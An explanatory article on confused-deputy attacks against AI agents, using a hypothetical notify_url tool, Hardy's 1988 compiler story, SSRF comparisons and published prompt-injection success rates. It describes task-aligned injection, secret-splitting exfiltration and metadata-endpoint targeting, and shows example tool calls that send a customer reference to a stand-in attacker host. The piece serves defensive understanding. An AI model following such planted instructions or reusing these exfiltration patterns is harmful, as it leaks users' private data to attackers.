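# Confused-deputy attacks on AI agents through URL notification tools

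## What is a confused deputy, and why can a tool-using agent be one?

A confused deputy is a program that is tricked into using its authority on behalf of someone who lacks that authority. The term comes from operating system design and is nearly forty years old. Security researchers now apply it to AI agents, which are language models that repeatedly choose an action, have ordinary software carry it out, and read the result. An agent often reads text written by strangers, such as web pages, emails and support tickets, and it can often send information out as well. If a stranger's text can determine what the agent sends and where, the stranger can use the agent's authority without needing a password.

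One small tool, here called notify_url, is enough to show the problem. It takes a web address and a message, and sends the message to that address. A developer might add it so that an agent can tell a team's chat channel that a job has finished. The name stands for any tool that sends a message to an address the model fills in.

### The compiler that overwrote the billing file

The term comes from Norm Hardy's *The Confused Deputy*, a short 1988 paper. Hardy tells a "nearly true story" from about eleven years earlier at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Tymshare kept a compiler in a system directory called SYSX. Users ran it on their own programs and could name a file to receive optional debugging output. Staff had also changed the compiler to record which language features people used, in a file called (SYSX)STAT. To let the compiler write there, they gave it a "home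 files license", which allowed it to write to any file in its home directory.

The company's billing records sat in the same directory, in a file called (SYSX)BILL. A user learned the name and gave it to the compiler as the debugging file. The compiler passed the name to the operating system and asked it to open the file for writing. The operating system checked that the compiler's licence allowed this and opened the file, and the compiler's debugging output replaced the billing records.

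Most of Hardy's paper is about how hard it is to say which line of code was wrong. Refusing file names in other directories would block users who had good reasons to put output there. Refusing anything in SYSX would block people with rights in that directory who might want output there, and nobody had thought of the name SYSX when the programmers wrote that code. The compiler could refuse (SYSX)BILL by name, but that was not the only sensitive file. On Hardy's account, the code was correct when the programmers wrote it and became wrong when somebody added the licence.

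Hardy argued that the compiler ran with authority from two sources, the user who started it and the licence, and could not tell the operating system which one a given request relied on. The engineers first added a system call that let a program choose between its two authorities, but they soon met applications that needed more than two. Hardy preferred to use capabilities, which combine the reference to a file and the permission to write to it in a single object. With this design, a user who may not write to the billing file cannot make the compiler write to it either.

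*Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) gave the underlying condition its usual name, ambient authority, which means authority that a program exercises without selecting it. The paper compares this to a world with doors but no keys, where a door opens when the right person walks up. Under Unix file permissions, for example, a program asks to open a file by name without presenting a credential, and the request succeeds or fails according to who is running the program. The paper adds that confusion becomes likely under a second condition, when one party names the resource and another supplies the permission. At Tymshare the user supplied the name (SYSX)BILL and the company supplied the licence, and agents involve almost exactly the same split.

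### The agent loop, and who holds the credentials

A language model cannot send a web request. As Anthropic's *How tool use works* describes the arrangement, the developer specifies which operations exist and what inputs they take, the model emits a structured request for one of them, other code runs the operation, and the result goes back into the conversation. That structured request, a tool name plus arguments, is a tool call. Siu, He and colleagues (2026), in *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security*, write the choice of each action as

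$$a_t \sim f(\cdot \mid p, \mathrm{Tr}_{t-1}, M_t)$$

where $f$ is the model, $p$ the user's prompt, $\mathrm{Tr}_{t-1}$ the record of all earlier actions and their results, and $M_t$ the agent's memory, which includes the developer's standing instructions. The model samples action $a_t$, the software executes it, and the result joins the record before the next step. So a web page that the agent fetched at step 3 is among the inputs to every choice from step 4 onward, including choices that have nothing to do with the page.

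The application around the model holds the credentials, not the model. Mellafe Zuvic (2026), in *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, lists what such an application may hold: a payment key, a mailbox, a token for a customer database, or just the ability to make web requests. He puts the model outside the trust boundary and treats it as "an untrusted parser and planner". Tools that a developer defines run in the developer's application, according to Anthropic's *Tool use with Claude*, while some ready-made ones, such as web search, run on the provider's machines. Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues (2026), in *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents*, point out that the component choosing the action, the user who asked for the task, the runtime with the credentials and the service receiving the request may be four distinct entities. The receiving service authenticates the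 caller but cannot tell who originally prompted the call.

Suppose a user asks an agent to work through last night's support tickets and then notify hooks.example.com. The model emits a call to notify_url with that address and a summary, and the company's software sends the summary from the company's network. The model can reach a different address just by writing a different string, and the call doesn't record who chose the string. The address corresponds to the file name in Hardy's example, and the company's network access, together with everything the agent has read, to the licence.

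Surapani and colleagues name three ways an agent differs from the compiler in Hardy's example. An agent's decision is probabilistic and depends on the prompt, whereas a compiler follows fixed code. The agent's authority comes through a chain of people, organisations, programs and services. The hostile request arrives inside a document or an email, whereas Hardy's user typed his at the command line. Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) add in *Silent Egress* that the doubt in the classical case is about which party the deputy serves, while with an agent it is about what that party intended, because the agent cannot reliably tell the user's request to fetch a page from instructions in the page.

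### Instructions and data in one stream

In indirect prompt injection, an attacker places instructions in content the agent reads while working, so that the model follows them as if its user had given them. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, recalls coining the broader term, prompt injection, for the mixing of trusted and untrusted text in one context. In a standard example, a job applicant hides an instruction in a CV for the recruiter's screening model to approve the candidate. The applicant doesn't need access to the recruiter's system to do this.

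Models are vulnerable to this because their usefulness depends on following instructions in text. According to Willison, a model cannot reliably weigh an instruction by its origin because all its input becomes one sequence of tokens, the fragments of text that a model processes. Lan and colleagues call this "context flattening": the application puts the developer's instructions, the user's request and the fetched page in one context window, which weakens the difference in rank between them. Text from a page can enter the window without the user asking for it, because many assistants fetch a preview of any link that appears in a conversation and include the preview's title and description.

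Not every instruction from outside is an attack. A user who asks an agent to follow a recipe wants it to use the oven temperature the recipe gives. Siu and colleagues therefore count an instruction as indirect prompt injection only if it came from an unauthenticated source and the resulting action does not serve the user's task. This condition correctly excludes the oven temperature, but it also excludes another of their examples, in which a recipe page tells the agent to pay for the ingredients with a particular card. They class this as a security violation because only the user may choose the card, even though the payment serves the task of buying dinner. The same problem arises with notify_url. When a support ticket gives a "new" address for the completion notice, sending the notice still serves the user's task, and only the destination has changed.

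People often compare prompt injection to SQL injection, an old attack on databases. A careless website pastes a visitor's text into a database command, and a visitor who types a fragment of the command language gets the database to run it. Developers solved this with parameterised queries, which keep the command and the visitor's text separate so that the database engine can never interpret the text as a command. In December 2025 David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), argued in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* that language models offer no equivalent. A database distinguishes instructions from data, but inside a model, he writes, "there is only ever 'next token'". Developers can train a model to prefer instructions over anything in the data that looks like one, or mark off the data with tags, but these methods try to add a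 distinction that the underlying technology does not have.

David C concludes that a language model is an "inherently confusable deputy". Engineers can repair an ordinary confused deputy, as Hardy proposed to do with capabilities, but with a model they can only lower the chance of confusion and limit the damage. If a system cannot tolerate the remaining risk, it may be a poor place for a model. Designers should assume that an attacker might be able to use every tool the model can call directly, and should rely on limits that ordinary software enforces. David C also cites a rule from an exchange between Willison and Baibhav Bista: when a model processes information from some party, its privileges should drop to that party's. This rule would severely restrict notify_url. An agent that has read a stranger's ticket would lose access to the tool, because the stranger had no right to call it.

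This argument, based on how models process text, gives good reason to expect that some attacks will always get through, but it doesn't show how many. David C himself writes only that there is "a good chance" that prompt injection will never be properly mitigated. A defence that fails one time in ten thousand and one that fails half the time are both "confusable" in his sense, although they are very different products for a designer.

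What an attacker can steal depends on the agent's other tools and the data it can reach. Willison names three conditions that together make data theft possible: the agent has access to private data, it reads untrusted content, and it can communicate with the outside. This kind of theft fails if any one of them is missing. The notify_url tool is enough to meet the third condition, and an agent that handles customer tickets usually meets the other two. Willison also counts loading an image or showing the user a link to click as outside communication, which developers might not expect. His conditions apply only to theft, though. An agent with no private data can still pass an attacker's link to someone who trusts the agent.

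### Two uses of the term

Writers on AI agents use "confused deputy" in both a strict and a broad sense, and a fix for the problem in one sense may not help with the problem in the other.

In the strict sense, which Siu and colleagues use, a confused deputy is an agent that accesses a resource at the request of an authenticated user who has no right to access it, although the agent does. For example, an employee acting as the attacker asks the company's assistant for everyone's salaries, and the assistant, which has access to the personnel database for administrative work, hands them over. *Proof-of-Continuity* (2026) gives a similar definition in four conditions (the user lacks the privilege, the deputy has it, the user sends a request, and the deputy uses the privilege as a result) and shows that Hardy's compiler meets them all. The four conditions don't settle whether the author of a web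 page could also count as the "user", with the page as the request.

Quarkslab, a security company, built a demonstration medical assistant with a tool that fetched a patient's history by number. A patient who asked for the records under somebody else's number got them. Telling the model to serve only the logged-in patient stopped the plain request, but not a request that Quarkslab hid in a web page file and had the assistant read. Changing the tool to compare the requested number with the logged-in patient worked. Quarkslab concludes that the confused deputy is an authorization problem and not an AI problem. This is mostly compatible with David C.'s view, since he also wants the limits outside the model, and Quarkslab's fix worked because the tool had a plain fact to check against.

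In the broad sense the less privileged party can be anyone whose text the agent reads. *Delegation Without Trust* (2026) describes an agent with legitimate authority that injected content turns toward an attacker's goal: "The agent is authorized; the use is not intended." Lan and colleagues, Mellafe Zuvic and David C all use the term this way. So does *Risks and Controls for Multi-Agent Systems* (2026) in effect, except that there the party without permission is another agent, which asks a better-equipped one to act for it. (The Model Context Protocol's *security best practices*, written for a standard that connects models to tools, also apply the name to a flaw in some proxy servers that use OAuth, a common system for granting access to accounts: they do not ask for the user's consent to each new client program, so an attacker can obtain access that the user never approved.)

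Attacks through notify_url are confused-deputy attacks in the broad sense but usually not in the strict one. The user who asked for the ticket summary was entitled to read the tickets and send a notice. Quarkslab's fix, which checks the user's own rights, does not help here because the call passes whatever address it contains. Hardy ran into the same difficulty when he considered having the compiler inspect file names, because users had legitimate reasons to write to files in other directories. Agent users likewise need to send messages to new addresses.

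## How does text in a retrieved page become a request to the attacker's server?

Suppose a user asks an agent to read a supplier's status page at status.supplier.example and notify the operations team if anything is down. The agent has two tools, notify_url and one that fetches web pages, and the developer's standing instructions give the team's channel as hooks.example.com. Someone has posted a comment under the supplier's latest incident report, telling systems that monitor the page to confirm that they received the notice at an address on confirm.example.net and to quote their customer reference. The comment reads like a note from the supplier, but the supplier didn't write it and doesn't own that address.

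The attacker can plant text in a page without breaking into anything. In *Mind the Web*, Shapira, Gandhi and colleagues (2025) attack agents that operate a web browser, assuming an attacker who can only post comments and reviews, place advertisements or edit shared content such as forum posts and documents. Lan and colleagues add that an attacker could reach a reputable page through a compromised advertising network or content delivery system.

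### One request, step by step

The agent first calls its fetch tool, and the software downloads the page and adds its text to the model's context. Nothing at this point separates the supplier's report from the comment beneath it. The browser agents that Shapira and colleagues describe also read everything visible on a page, and those that work from screenshots read text inside images too. Lan and colleagues' test system passed on the page's raw text, including HTML comments that a browser never displays. With a system like that, the attacker could hide the note from people reading the status page.

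A crude injection tells the model to ignore its previous instructions, which openly conflicts with the user's request. Shapira and colleagues avoid this conflict with task-aligned injection, which presents the instruction as a helpful suggestion, a system notice or a refinement of the task. Their examples include a note that this version of the site is out of date, and a false completion message that suggests the agent still has something to verify. In the supplier example, the user wanted a notification about the status page, and confirming receipt is another notification about the same page. The user also didn't list the steps, so the model has to plan them itself. Shapira and colleagues argue that a planted step fits most easily into open-ended requests like this.

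Injected text can also work without a disguise. Lan and colleagues labelled theirs an important system instruction, and the small model they tested usually followed it.

If the model accepts the comment as part of the job, it writes two calls:

```
notify_url(url="https://hooks.example.com/ops",
           message="Supplier reports degraded service since 02:10.")
notify_url(url="https://confirm.example.net/receipt",
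           message="Notice received. Customer reference: 48213.")
```

The attacker wrote the address in the second call, and the model copied it. The attacker did not know the customer reference and could not see the context, but a description of the reference was enough for the model to find it and insert it. Similarly, in the example test page from Lan and colleagues, the web address contains a placeholder for the model to fill with an API key, a secret that identifies one program to another. The attacker also doesn't need to know that the tool is called notify_url, because the model can match a request to "confirm receipt" with a tool that can do it.

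Next, the software checks the calls. Mellafe Zuvic, who read the source code of three widely used agent toolkits, reports that by default the toolkits check whether the tool is available and whether the arguments have the right form. Both addresses are well-formed strings, so both calls pass. The software sends the message from the company's network, and the attacker's server receives it along with the time and its source network address. The tool then returns a short success result, and the model continues its task.

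The user sees an accurate reply saying that the supplier reports degraded service and that the operations team knows. The final answer was similarly harmless in 95% of the successful attacks that Lan and colleagues ran. The user would have to open the log of tool calls to notice anything, and even there a confirmation of receipt looks routine. Lan and colleagues raise this as an objection to asking users to approve every request, because most people cannot judge whether a "connectivity verification" is genuine.

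### What the attacker gains

The attacker learns something even if the message is empty. If the address appears only in the planted comment, a notification sent there means an agent probably read the page and followed the text, and the sender's network address may identify the company. The agent that Lan and colleagues tested never contacted their collecting server in 120 control runs with harmless pages, so contact can be a very clear signal. Contact can also happen without data theft. In one of their configurations, 29 of 30 runs contacted the server, but only 26 included sensitive data in the first request. An attacker could therefore start with an innocuous request for confirmation and save more suspicious instructions for the companies whose agents respond.

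Data can leave in any part of the request that the model writes. The message field of notify_url can hold the most text, but the address alone is enough, because a web address can contain arbitrary text in its path or in the query string after a question mark. Removing the message field would not make the tool safe. The tool that fetches pages also takes an address, so the agent could leak the customer reference by fetching a page whose address contains it.

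Lan and colleagues also tested an instruction to split the secret into four pieces and send each one in a separate numbered request. Each request then contains only a short fragment that resembles ordinary usage data, so a filter that searches for the whole secret would miss it. The share of runs with sensitive data in the first request fell from 97% to 26%, partly because the longer instruction made the attack fail more often. They also report that 16% of runs leaked data somewhere in the first three requests. That share cannot be lower than the share for the first request alone, so at least one of the two figures must be wrong.

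The server's reply can bring new instructions. The result of notify_url goes into the agent's context, so if the developer chose to include the full reply, the attacker can put any text there. The attacker has to write a comment on a status page in advance and in public, whereas a reply can depend on what the agent just sent. After receiving the customer reference, for example, the server could answer that the receipt is incomplete without a contract number. MITRE's *CWE-918*, an entry in a widely used catalogue of software weaknesses, lists a related flaw in a framework for building on language models. Prompt injection could force the service to retrieve data from any address, and the retrieved content could then enter later tasks. If notify_url returned only "delivered" or "failed", the text of the attacker's reply would not reach the context.

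The attacker can also name an address inside the company's network, which outsiders cannot reach but the agent's software can. MITRE lists administration panels, services running on the same machine and cloud metadata endpoints as typical targets. A metadata endpoint is an internal address where a cloud server looks up information about itself. According to Knowledge Space's *CWE-918*, a set of anonymous study notes, the endpoint can return the server's credentials, sometimes without requiring authentication. GCVE's *CWE-918*, another catalogue entry, adds that a forged request runs with the server's privileges.

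Stealing credentials this way through notify_url takes more steps than the attack in the supplier example. The internal service has to respond to the kind of request the tool sends, the tool has to return the reply to the model, and the model has to make a second call that sends the reply to the attacker. Causing damage can take only one call if an internal service acts on any message from inside the network, because the attacker doesn't need to see the reply.

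### Pages that nobody asked the agent to read

In the supplier example, the user asked for the page. Lan and colleagues are more worried about cases where the user did not, which they call implicit prompt injection. Suppose a coworker pastes a link into a conversation, and the user asks the agent to draft a polite reply. If the agent previews links automatically, the page's title, description and Open Graph tags (hidden fields that specify what other sites show in a preview) enter the context. A person who opens the link sees an ordinary article, because browsers don't display most of these fields. The attacker may not need a coworker to share the link. Lan and colleagues also mention pages that attackers push up the search rankings, and addresses that differ from a well-known one by a single typo.

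Fetching a link preview sends a request to the attacker's server before the model has selected an action. The attacker learns that some software handled the link, but not yet whether an agent will follow the instructions in the text.

The experiment by Lan and colleagues only partly covers this case. They put instructions in page titles and descriptions, and the agent followed them almost every time when the task was to send the data in one piece. But in every run the user had asked the agent to summarise the page. The results therefore show that hidden fields deliver instructions to the model about as well as body text does, but not how often an agent would act on a preview while working on something unrelated. That rate might well be lower, since the instruction would no longer fit the user's task.

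### Comparison with SSRF and cross-site request forgery

Web developers have long known a similar problem as server-side request forgery (SSRF). MITRE defines it as a web server retrieving the contents of a URL it received from elsewhere without making sure that the request goes to the expected destination. MITRE's sample code takes a URL from a visitor's request and passes it straight to a download function. The software behind notify_url does much the same with a URL from the model. MITRE classes SSRF as a kind of "Unintended Proxy or Intermediary", which is close to Hardy's idea of a confused deputy. It also lists SSRF as often prevalent in AI and machine-learning technology.

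The model changes how the attacker's address gets into the request. In ordinary SSRF, the attacker has to find the input that feeds the download function, and whatever they put there always reaches that function. With an agent, the attacker writes ordinary prose, and the model decides whether to make a request, which tool to use and what to put in it. Lan and colleagues call this "LLM-mediated SSRF" and consider it more powerful than the classical kind. The attacker doesn't need to know how the tools work, the same text can succeed against agents that are built differently, and the model can add data the attacker has never seen.

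They are right about the reach of the attack, but it is less reliable than exploiting an ordinary SSRF flaw. An attacker who finds an SSRF flaw can use it until a developer fixes it, while a model may follow a planted comment only some of the time or not at all. How much this protects anyone depends on how easily the attacker can try again, and posting the same comment on many pages takes very little effort.

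Finding the flaw in advance is also harder. MITRE rates automated code analysis as highly effective against SSRF because it can trace a path from an outside input to the function that sends the request. In an agent, that path runs through the model, which takes in every input and produces every argument. An analysis tool that cannot trace data through the model will miss the connection, while one that assumes any input can influence any argument will flag every outbound tool the agent has. Those flags are correct, but they don't help a developer decide which calls to allow.

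In cross-site request forgery, the confused deputy is a browser instead of a server. A hostile website makes a visitor's browser send a request to another site where the visitor is logged in, such as a bank. The browser attaches the visitor's login cookie, which gives the request the visitor's authority, so the bank cannot tell it from one the visitor meant to make.

The usual defence is for the bank to put an unpredictable token in its own forms and refuse any submission that lacks it. This works because browsers stop the hostile site from reading the bank's pages, where the token is. An agent that operates a browser can get around this by reading the hostile page, opening the bank's real form with a valid token inside, and submitting it. Some of the agents that Shapira and colleagues studied run as browser extensions with direct access to the user's active sessions, so the bank would receive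 a normal form from a logged-in user. Misuse of a plain notify_url tool that sends no login cookies is closer to SSRF than to this attack.

### Real tools that take a destination

The simplest real equivalent of notify_url is a general web request tool, like the one in Lan and colleagues' test system, which could both fetch pages and send data. Other tools include an address among several arguments, where it is easier to overlook. Mellafe Zuvic found that the public code of the Stripe Agent Toolkit, which lets agents work with the payment company Stripe, forwards a redirect address from the model along with the amount, currency and customer. He doesn't claim to know what further checks Stripe's servers may make. A redirect address normally determines where the customer's browser goes after a payment, so a false one would send the customer to the attacker's site. That makes it more useful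 for phishing than for stealing the agent's data.

Webhooks resemble notify_url more closely. A webhook is an address that one program gives another for receiving messages when something happens. The Agent2Agent protocol (A2A), which lets one agent hand a task to another, uses webhooks for tasks that run for minutes or days. According to the A2A documentation, the client supplies an address, and the remote agent sends a notification there when the task finishes, fails or needs more input. The notification may contain only the task's number and new state, or the whole task. In version 1.0, the address is a required field of the notification settings, which Google Cloud's *Package lf.a2a.v1* describes as the URL "where the notification should be sent".

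A false address could do more harm in an A2A webhook registration than in a single notify_url call. Ghumare (2026) explains in *A2A v1.0*, a guide for developers, that once a client has registered a webhook for a task, every later update goes to it. An attacker whose address was registered could therefore follow the task until it finished. The attack works only if the developer has let the language model write the address, for example by offering webhook registration as a tool. The protocol doesn't require this, and in a careful design the client's ordinary code would fill in the address from a fixed setting.

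A2A clients also receive addresses from outside. Each agent publishes an "agent card" that describes its skills and gives the address where clients can send it work. Ghumare warns that the card's text enters the client model's context and may contain injected instructions. An attacker can also copy a trusted card and change only the address. Ghumare recommends checking the card's digital signature, but notes that a valid signature doesn't show whether the organisation behind it should be given the work.

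The A2A documentation anticipates part of the problem. It warns that a malicious client could supply a webhook address that points to an internal service, or use the remote agent to flood a third party with traffic. The A2A specification recommends, but does not require, that agents validate webhook addresses and reject private and local ones (the word it uses is "SHOULD"). JMAP, an email protocol, is stricter about its own push notifications and says the server "MUST" make sure that the address is externally resolvable. An Apache issue report for the James mail server, about code that was not yet in a release, quotes this rule and adds, "We do not do that." a2akit's *Push Notifications*, the documentation of a small A2A framework, lists an allowlist and a blocklist of webhook hosts, both empty by default.

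Rejecting private addresses protects internal services, but it would still allow confirm.example.net, which is a public address. The A2A documentation also suggests an ownership check, in which the server sends a random token to the proposed address and checks that the receiver returns it. An internal service or an uninvolved company would normally fail this check, but the attacker's server would pass because the attacker owns the address.

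## How often do agents obey such text?

Published rates range from 0% to 100%, depending on the model, the wording of the planted text, the channel it arrives through, how many tries the attacker gets, and whether researchers count attempts, completed requests or data leaks. In the supplier example, the agent makes an attempt when it writes a call to confirm.example.net. The request is complete when the attacker's server receives it, and it leaks data only if the message contains something private, such as the customer reference. A test that intercepts every call can measure only attempts. A company whose network blocks the address might see many attempts without any data leaking.

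*InjecAgent* (Zhan, Liang and colleagues, 2024), an early benchmark, found that an agent built on GPT-4 followed planted instructions in 24% of cases, and in 47% when the instructions included a stock phrase telling it to ignore everything before them. These rates are now out of date. The benchmark scored fetching private data and sending it on as separate steps, and an agent that had fetched the data almost always sent it.

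### A small model that almost always complied

Lan and colleagues measured completed requests and leaks directly, by recording what reached a server that played the attacker. Their agent ran on qwen2.5:7b, a small open model that they hosted themselves. They planted an instruction in the body, description fields, title or link text of a web page, telling the agent to send an API key to that server. The agent reached the page directly or through redirects, and the instruction asked for the key whole or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 resulting configurations 30 times.

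The server received at least one request in 423 of the 480 runs, a rate of 0.88. The paper's abstract gives the rate as 0.89, which matches the redirected pages alone (213 of 240). Direct pages had a similar rate (210 of 240), as expected, since the model reads the same text either way.

Splitting the key made a much bigger difference. The table gives the number of runs out of 60 for each position of the text, combining direct and redirected delivery.

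| Position of the instruction | Whole key: contact | Whole key: data in first request | Split key: contact | Split key: data in first request |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Page body | 60 | 60 | 48 | 14 |
| Description fields | 58 | 54 | 39 | 8 |
| Title | 60 | 58 | 52 | 11 |
| Link text | 60 | 60 | 46 | 30 |
| All positions (of 240) | 238 | 232 | 185 | 63 |

Lan and colleagues treat the fall in the last column as a gain in stealth, because each request carries less. But their definition counts even a single fragment of the key as sensitive data, so a split attack that worked should score on its first request just as a whole-key attack does. In 122 of the 185 split runs that reached the server, the scoring found nothing sensitive in the first request. Either the scoring missed four-character fragments, or the small model usually failed to send a proper fragment. If the model failed, many of these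 attacks were unsuccessful rather than stealthy.

Lan and colleagues define a completion rate, the share of runs in which all four pieces arrived, but give no value for it, so their results don't show how often an attacker could have rebuilt the key. They also give two conflicting leak rates for split runs, 26.3% for the first request and 15.8% for the first three. The 26.3% matches the configuration results, so the 15.8% is probably wrong.

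Some of their explanations are also doubtful. They suggest that long contexts dilute a model's attention to complicated instructions, but their software cut each field of the page to 500 characters, so the contexts were short. Their other suggestion, that the model loses track of pieces and numbers over several calls, fits the setup better. They conclude that splitting is most viable in the page body, but in their results, instructions in the title produced more contacts than those in the body, and instructions in link text leaked data more than twice as often as those in the body.

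None of the 120 control runs contacted the attacker's address, which is compatible with a true rate of up to about 2.5%. But a zero was close to guaranteed, because nothing on a harmless page would have given the model that address. The control runs show that the planted text caused the contacts, but they don't show how often an agent sends data to the wrong place when nobody is attacking it.

The 88% rate is hard to apply to a real product because Lan and colleagues placed the key directly in the model's context, and the standing instructions contained only the format for tool calls. When they added an explicit warning against following web content, the agent still contacted the server in two thirds of runs. They call their rates a lower bound because the attack texts were simple, but they also describe the setup as favourable to the attacker. Both descriptions are fair, and because a favourable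 setup could raise the rate while simple attacks lower it, 88% is not a reliable lower or upper bound. The researchers also argue that larger models could do worse because these models use tools more reliably and follow instructions more closely.

### Stronger models, better disguises and other channels

Evidence from larger models mostly goes against that prediction. Mellafe Zuvic summarises a sweep of 27 models in which 12 low-cost models attempted the attacker's action in 60.3% of trials on average, and 15 flagship models in 18.9%. The tools ran in a sandbox, so these figures count only attempts, and no real data left it. He gives no confidence intervals for the two averages, and rates for individual models varied widely. gpt-4o-mini and glm-4.5-air made the attempt in every trial, glm-5.2 in 8.7%, and gemini-3.1-pro-preview in none.

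Price is only a rough measure of capability, and the flagships may have had more security training. The gap matters to developers whatever its cause, because a cheap model is tempting for an agent that reads thousands of support tickets a day. Mellafe Zuvic infers this from the economics and doesn't claim to know which models companies run.

All of these rates come from task-aligned text, which presents the attacker's action as part of the user's job. In separate runs, he compared it with a crude request for the same action. On glm-4.7, the crude version worked in 13 of 46 trials (28.3%) and the task-aligned version worked in all 46. On mistral-large, successes rose from 2 of 74 to 34 of 74. Gemma-3-12b-it, a small open model, would have seemed immune to a developer who tried only the crude text, which worked in 0 of 70 trials, but the task-aligned text worked in 40 of 70.

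Task-aligned text does not always work better than crude text. With Latam-GPT, a version of Llama 3.1 adapted for Latin America, it raised the rate from 32% to 52% in English but lowered it from 24% to 4% in Spanish. Mellafe Zuvic warns that he ran the model in compressed form and had it write tool calls as plain text, so formatting failures could explain some of this. Yet in another Spanish scenario, about a payment agent, the same model attempted an unauthorised payout in all 10 trials. One person wrote the test cases comparing crude and task-aligned text, and they cover only one delivery route and single-turn tasks, so cases written by someone else could easily produce different numbers.

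In *LivePI*, Zhao, Bhaskar and Dobriban (2026) tested Gemini 3.1 Pro and four other models inside OpenClaw, an agent that people run on their own machines with access to their accounts. They set it up on a live virtual server with test accounts for email and chat and a cryptocurrency wallet holding a small balance. They counted an attack as a success only if the planted text affected the run and the attacker's goal was achieved. Where a goal left traces, such as a sent email or a transaction record, they checked for those.

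Of the five models, Gemini 3.1 Pro had the highest attack success rate, at 29.6% (50 of 169 cases), and Claude Opus 4.6 had the lowest, at 10.7% (18 cases). Gemini's preview version had scored zero in Mellafe Zuvic's sweep, but that test used different attacks and agent software, and the two versions of the model may also differ slightly. Even so, a developer who chose Gemini because of that zero would have badly underestimated its vulnerability in OpenClaw.

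The channel mattered at least as much as the model. All 15 attacks through group chats succeeded against all five models. Zhao and colleagues traced this to OpenClaw's code, which labels tool output as tool results but labels messages from anyone in a group as the user's words. Training a model to distrust retrieved text would not obviously help, because nothing marks these messages as retrieved. Excluding group chats, attacks succeeded in 3 of 154 cases (about 2%) against Claude Opus 4.6 and 35 of 154 (about 23%) against Gemini 3.1 Pro.

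The nearest match to the supplier's status page is a set of 50 cases in which the agent fetched a public tutorial from the web. Four of the five models resisted the attack in every case, and Gemini 3.1 Pro obeyed the attack text in 10. Attacks through email were more effective, with success rates between 2% and 20%, and those through local files ranged from 0% to 50%. Zhao and colleagues report no repeated runs or confidence intervals, and their judge was a language model from the same family as one of the tested models. They fixed the attack texts in advance, so an attacker who could revise a failed text might do better.

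### What developers report for their newest models

Developers now publish injection results in system cards, the reports that accompany new models. Several use a benchmark from Gray Swan, a security firm that collects attacks. According to OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026), Gray Swan tried 1,810 of these attacks on GPT-6 Astra. An attacker had an estimated 8.5% chance of succeeding within 15 attempts at a scenario, compared with 27.0% for the earlier GPT-5.6 Sol. In OpenAI's own automated tests, the model resisted 99.79% of planted instructions, up from 96.23%.

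Anthropic reports lower rates for its own models. Schneier on Security's *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (2026) quotes results for Claude Opus 5, released in July 2026, on a Gray Swan benchmark. Attackers succeeded 0.2% of the time with one attempt and 2.0% within 15 attempts, compared with 0.5% and 5.5% for the previous model, Opus 4.8. In September, Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 and Claude Mythos 5.1 described Mythos 5.1 as its most robust model so far on the external injection benchmark.

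The 8.5% for Astra and the 2.0% for Opus 5 are not directly comparable. GPT-5.6 Sol scored 27.0% in OpenAI's results and 20.0% in Anthropic's, so the attacks or the conditions must have differed. Opus 5's rate was a tenth of Sol's in Anthropic's results, and Astra's was about a third of Sol's in OpenAI's, which suggests that Opus 5 is ahead, though the comparison is rough. OpenAI's evaluation also covered more than leaks, since the planted text could aim at deleting data, compromising a system or making a payment.

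Curated attacks are also a limited test because people wrote them before the newest models came out, and a real attacker can adapt. Anthropic also tests with an adaptive attacker, which rewrites its text after seeing what the model does. VentureBeat, citing the Opus 4.8 card, reports that this attacker succeeded against the browser agent in 31.5% of attempts without Anthropic's extra safeguards and 0.5% with them. For Opus 5, the rate was 0% across 129 browser scenarios, according to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*. If those scenarios were a random sample of what attackers might try, a true rate of up to about 2.3% would still be consistent with that result.

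These adaptive tests are the developer's own. LivePI is independent, but it used fixed texts on models that are now several versions old. Gray Swan's benchmark is also external, but it was built from attacks collected earlier. An outside team that adapted its attacks to Astra or Opus 5 could therefore find higher rates than any of these tests did.

Another experiment in OpenAI's card is relevant to notify_url. An agent with a browsing task could reach a simulated message board that held instructions to disclose private information or approve illicit access. GPT-5.6 Sol followed the instructions in 52% of samples. Astra engaged with the board in 27% of samples but never followed the instructions. OpenAI revised this test repeatedly to provoke the behaviour, so the 52% is not an estimate for ordinary use. If OpenAI used Sol when revising the test, the comparison is also biased in Astra's favour.

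In the other, OpenAI gave agents workplace tasks with ambiguous instructions and confusing permissions. Astra caused some unintended outcome, such as a leak or an unauthorised payment, in 3.4% of them. Its rate for data exfiltration was 4.3%, or 4.5% when it also had a policy on when to ask the user for confirmation. Since 4.3% is higher than the overall rate, it presumably covers only the tasks that tested for leaks. OpenAI made the tasks deliberately difficult, but the failures came from confusion about the work. An agent with notify_url can evidently leak data without an attacker, even though none did in Lan and colleagues' control runs.

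### What a low rate means over many attempts

An attacker who can try again needs only one success. If each attempt succeeds with probability $p$ and the attempts are independent, the chance of at least one success in $n$ attempts is

$$P_n = 1 - (1 - p)^n$$

The table applies this to four rates. The single-attempt rate was 0.2% for Claude Opus 5 and 4.7% for the older Claude Opus 4.5. The other two rates are for comparison.

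| Success rate per attempt | 10 attempts | 100 attempts | 1,000 attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0.01% | 0.1% | 1.0% | 9.5% |
| 0.2% | 2.0% | 18% | 86% |
| 1% | 9.6% | 63% | over 99.9% |
| 4.7% | 38% | 99% | over 99.9% |

At a success rate of 0.2%, an attacker would need about 350 attempts for an even chance of succeeding at least once. A script could post that many comments or support tickets in minutes if nobody stopped it.

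Measured success rates grow more slowly than predicted by the formula, which assumes that attempts are independent. For Opus 4.5, The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports 4.7% after one attempt, 33.6% after ten and 63% after a hundred, while the formula gives 38% after ten and 99% after a hundred. VentureBeat reports that, without safeguards, attacks on an agent using Opus 4.6 on a graphical interface succeeded 17.8% of the time at first and 78.6% by the 200th attempt, when the formula gives nearly 100%. For Opus 5, the measured rate within 15 attempts was 2.0%, compared with 3.0% from the formula.

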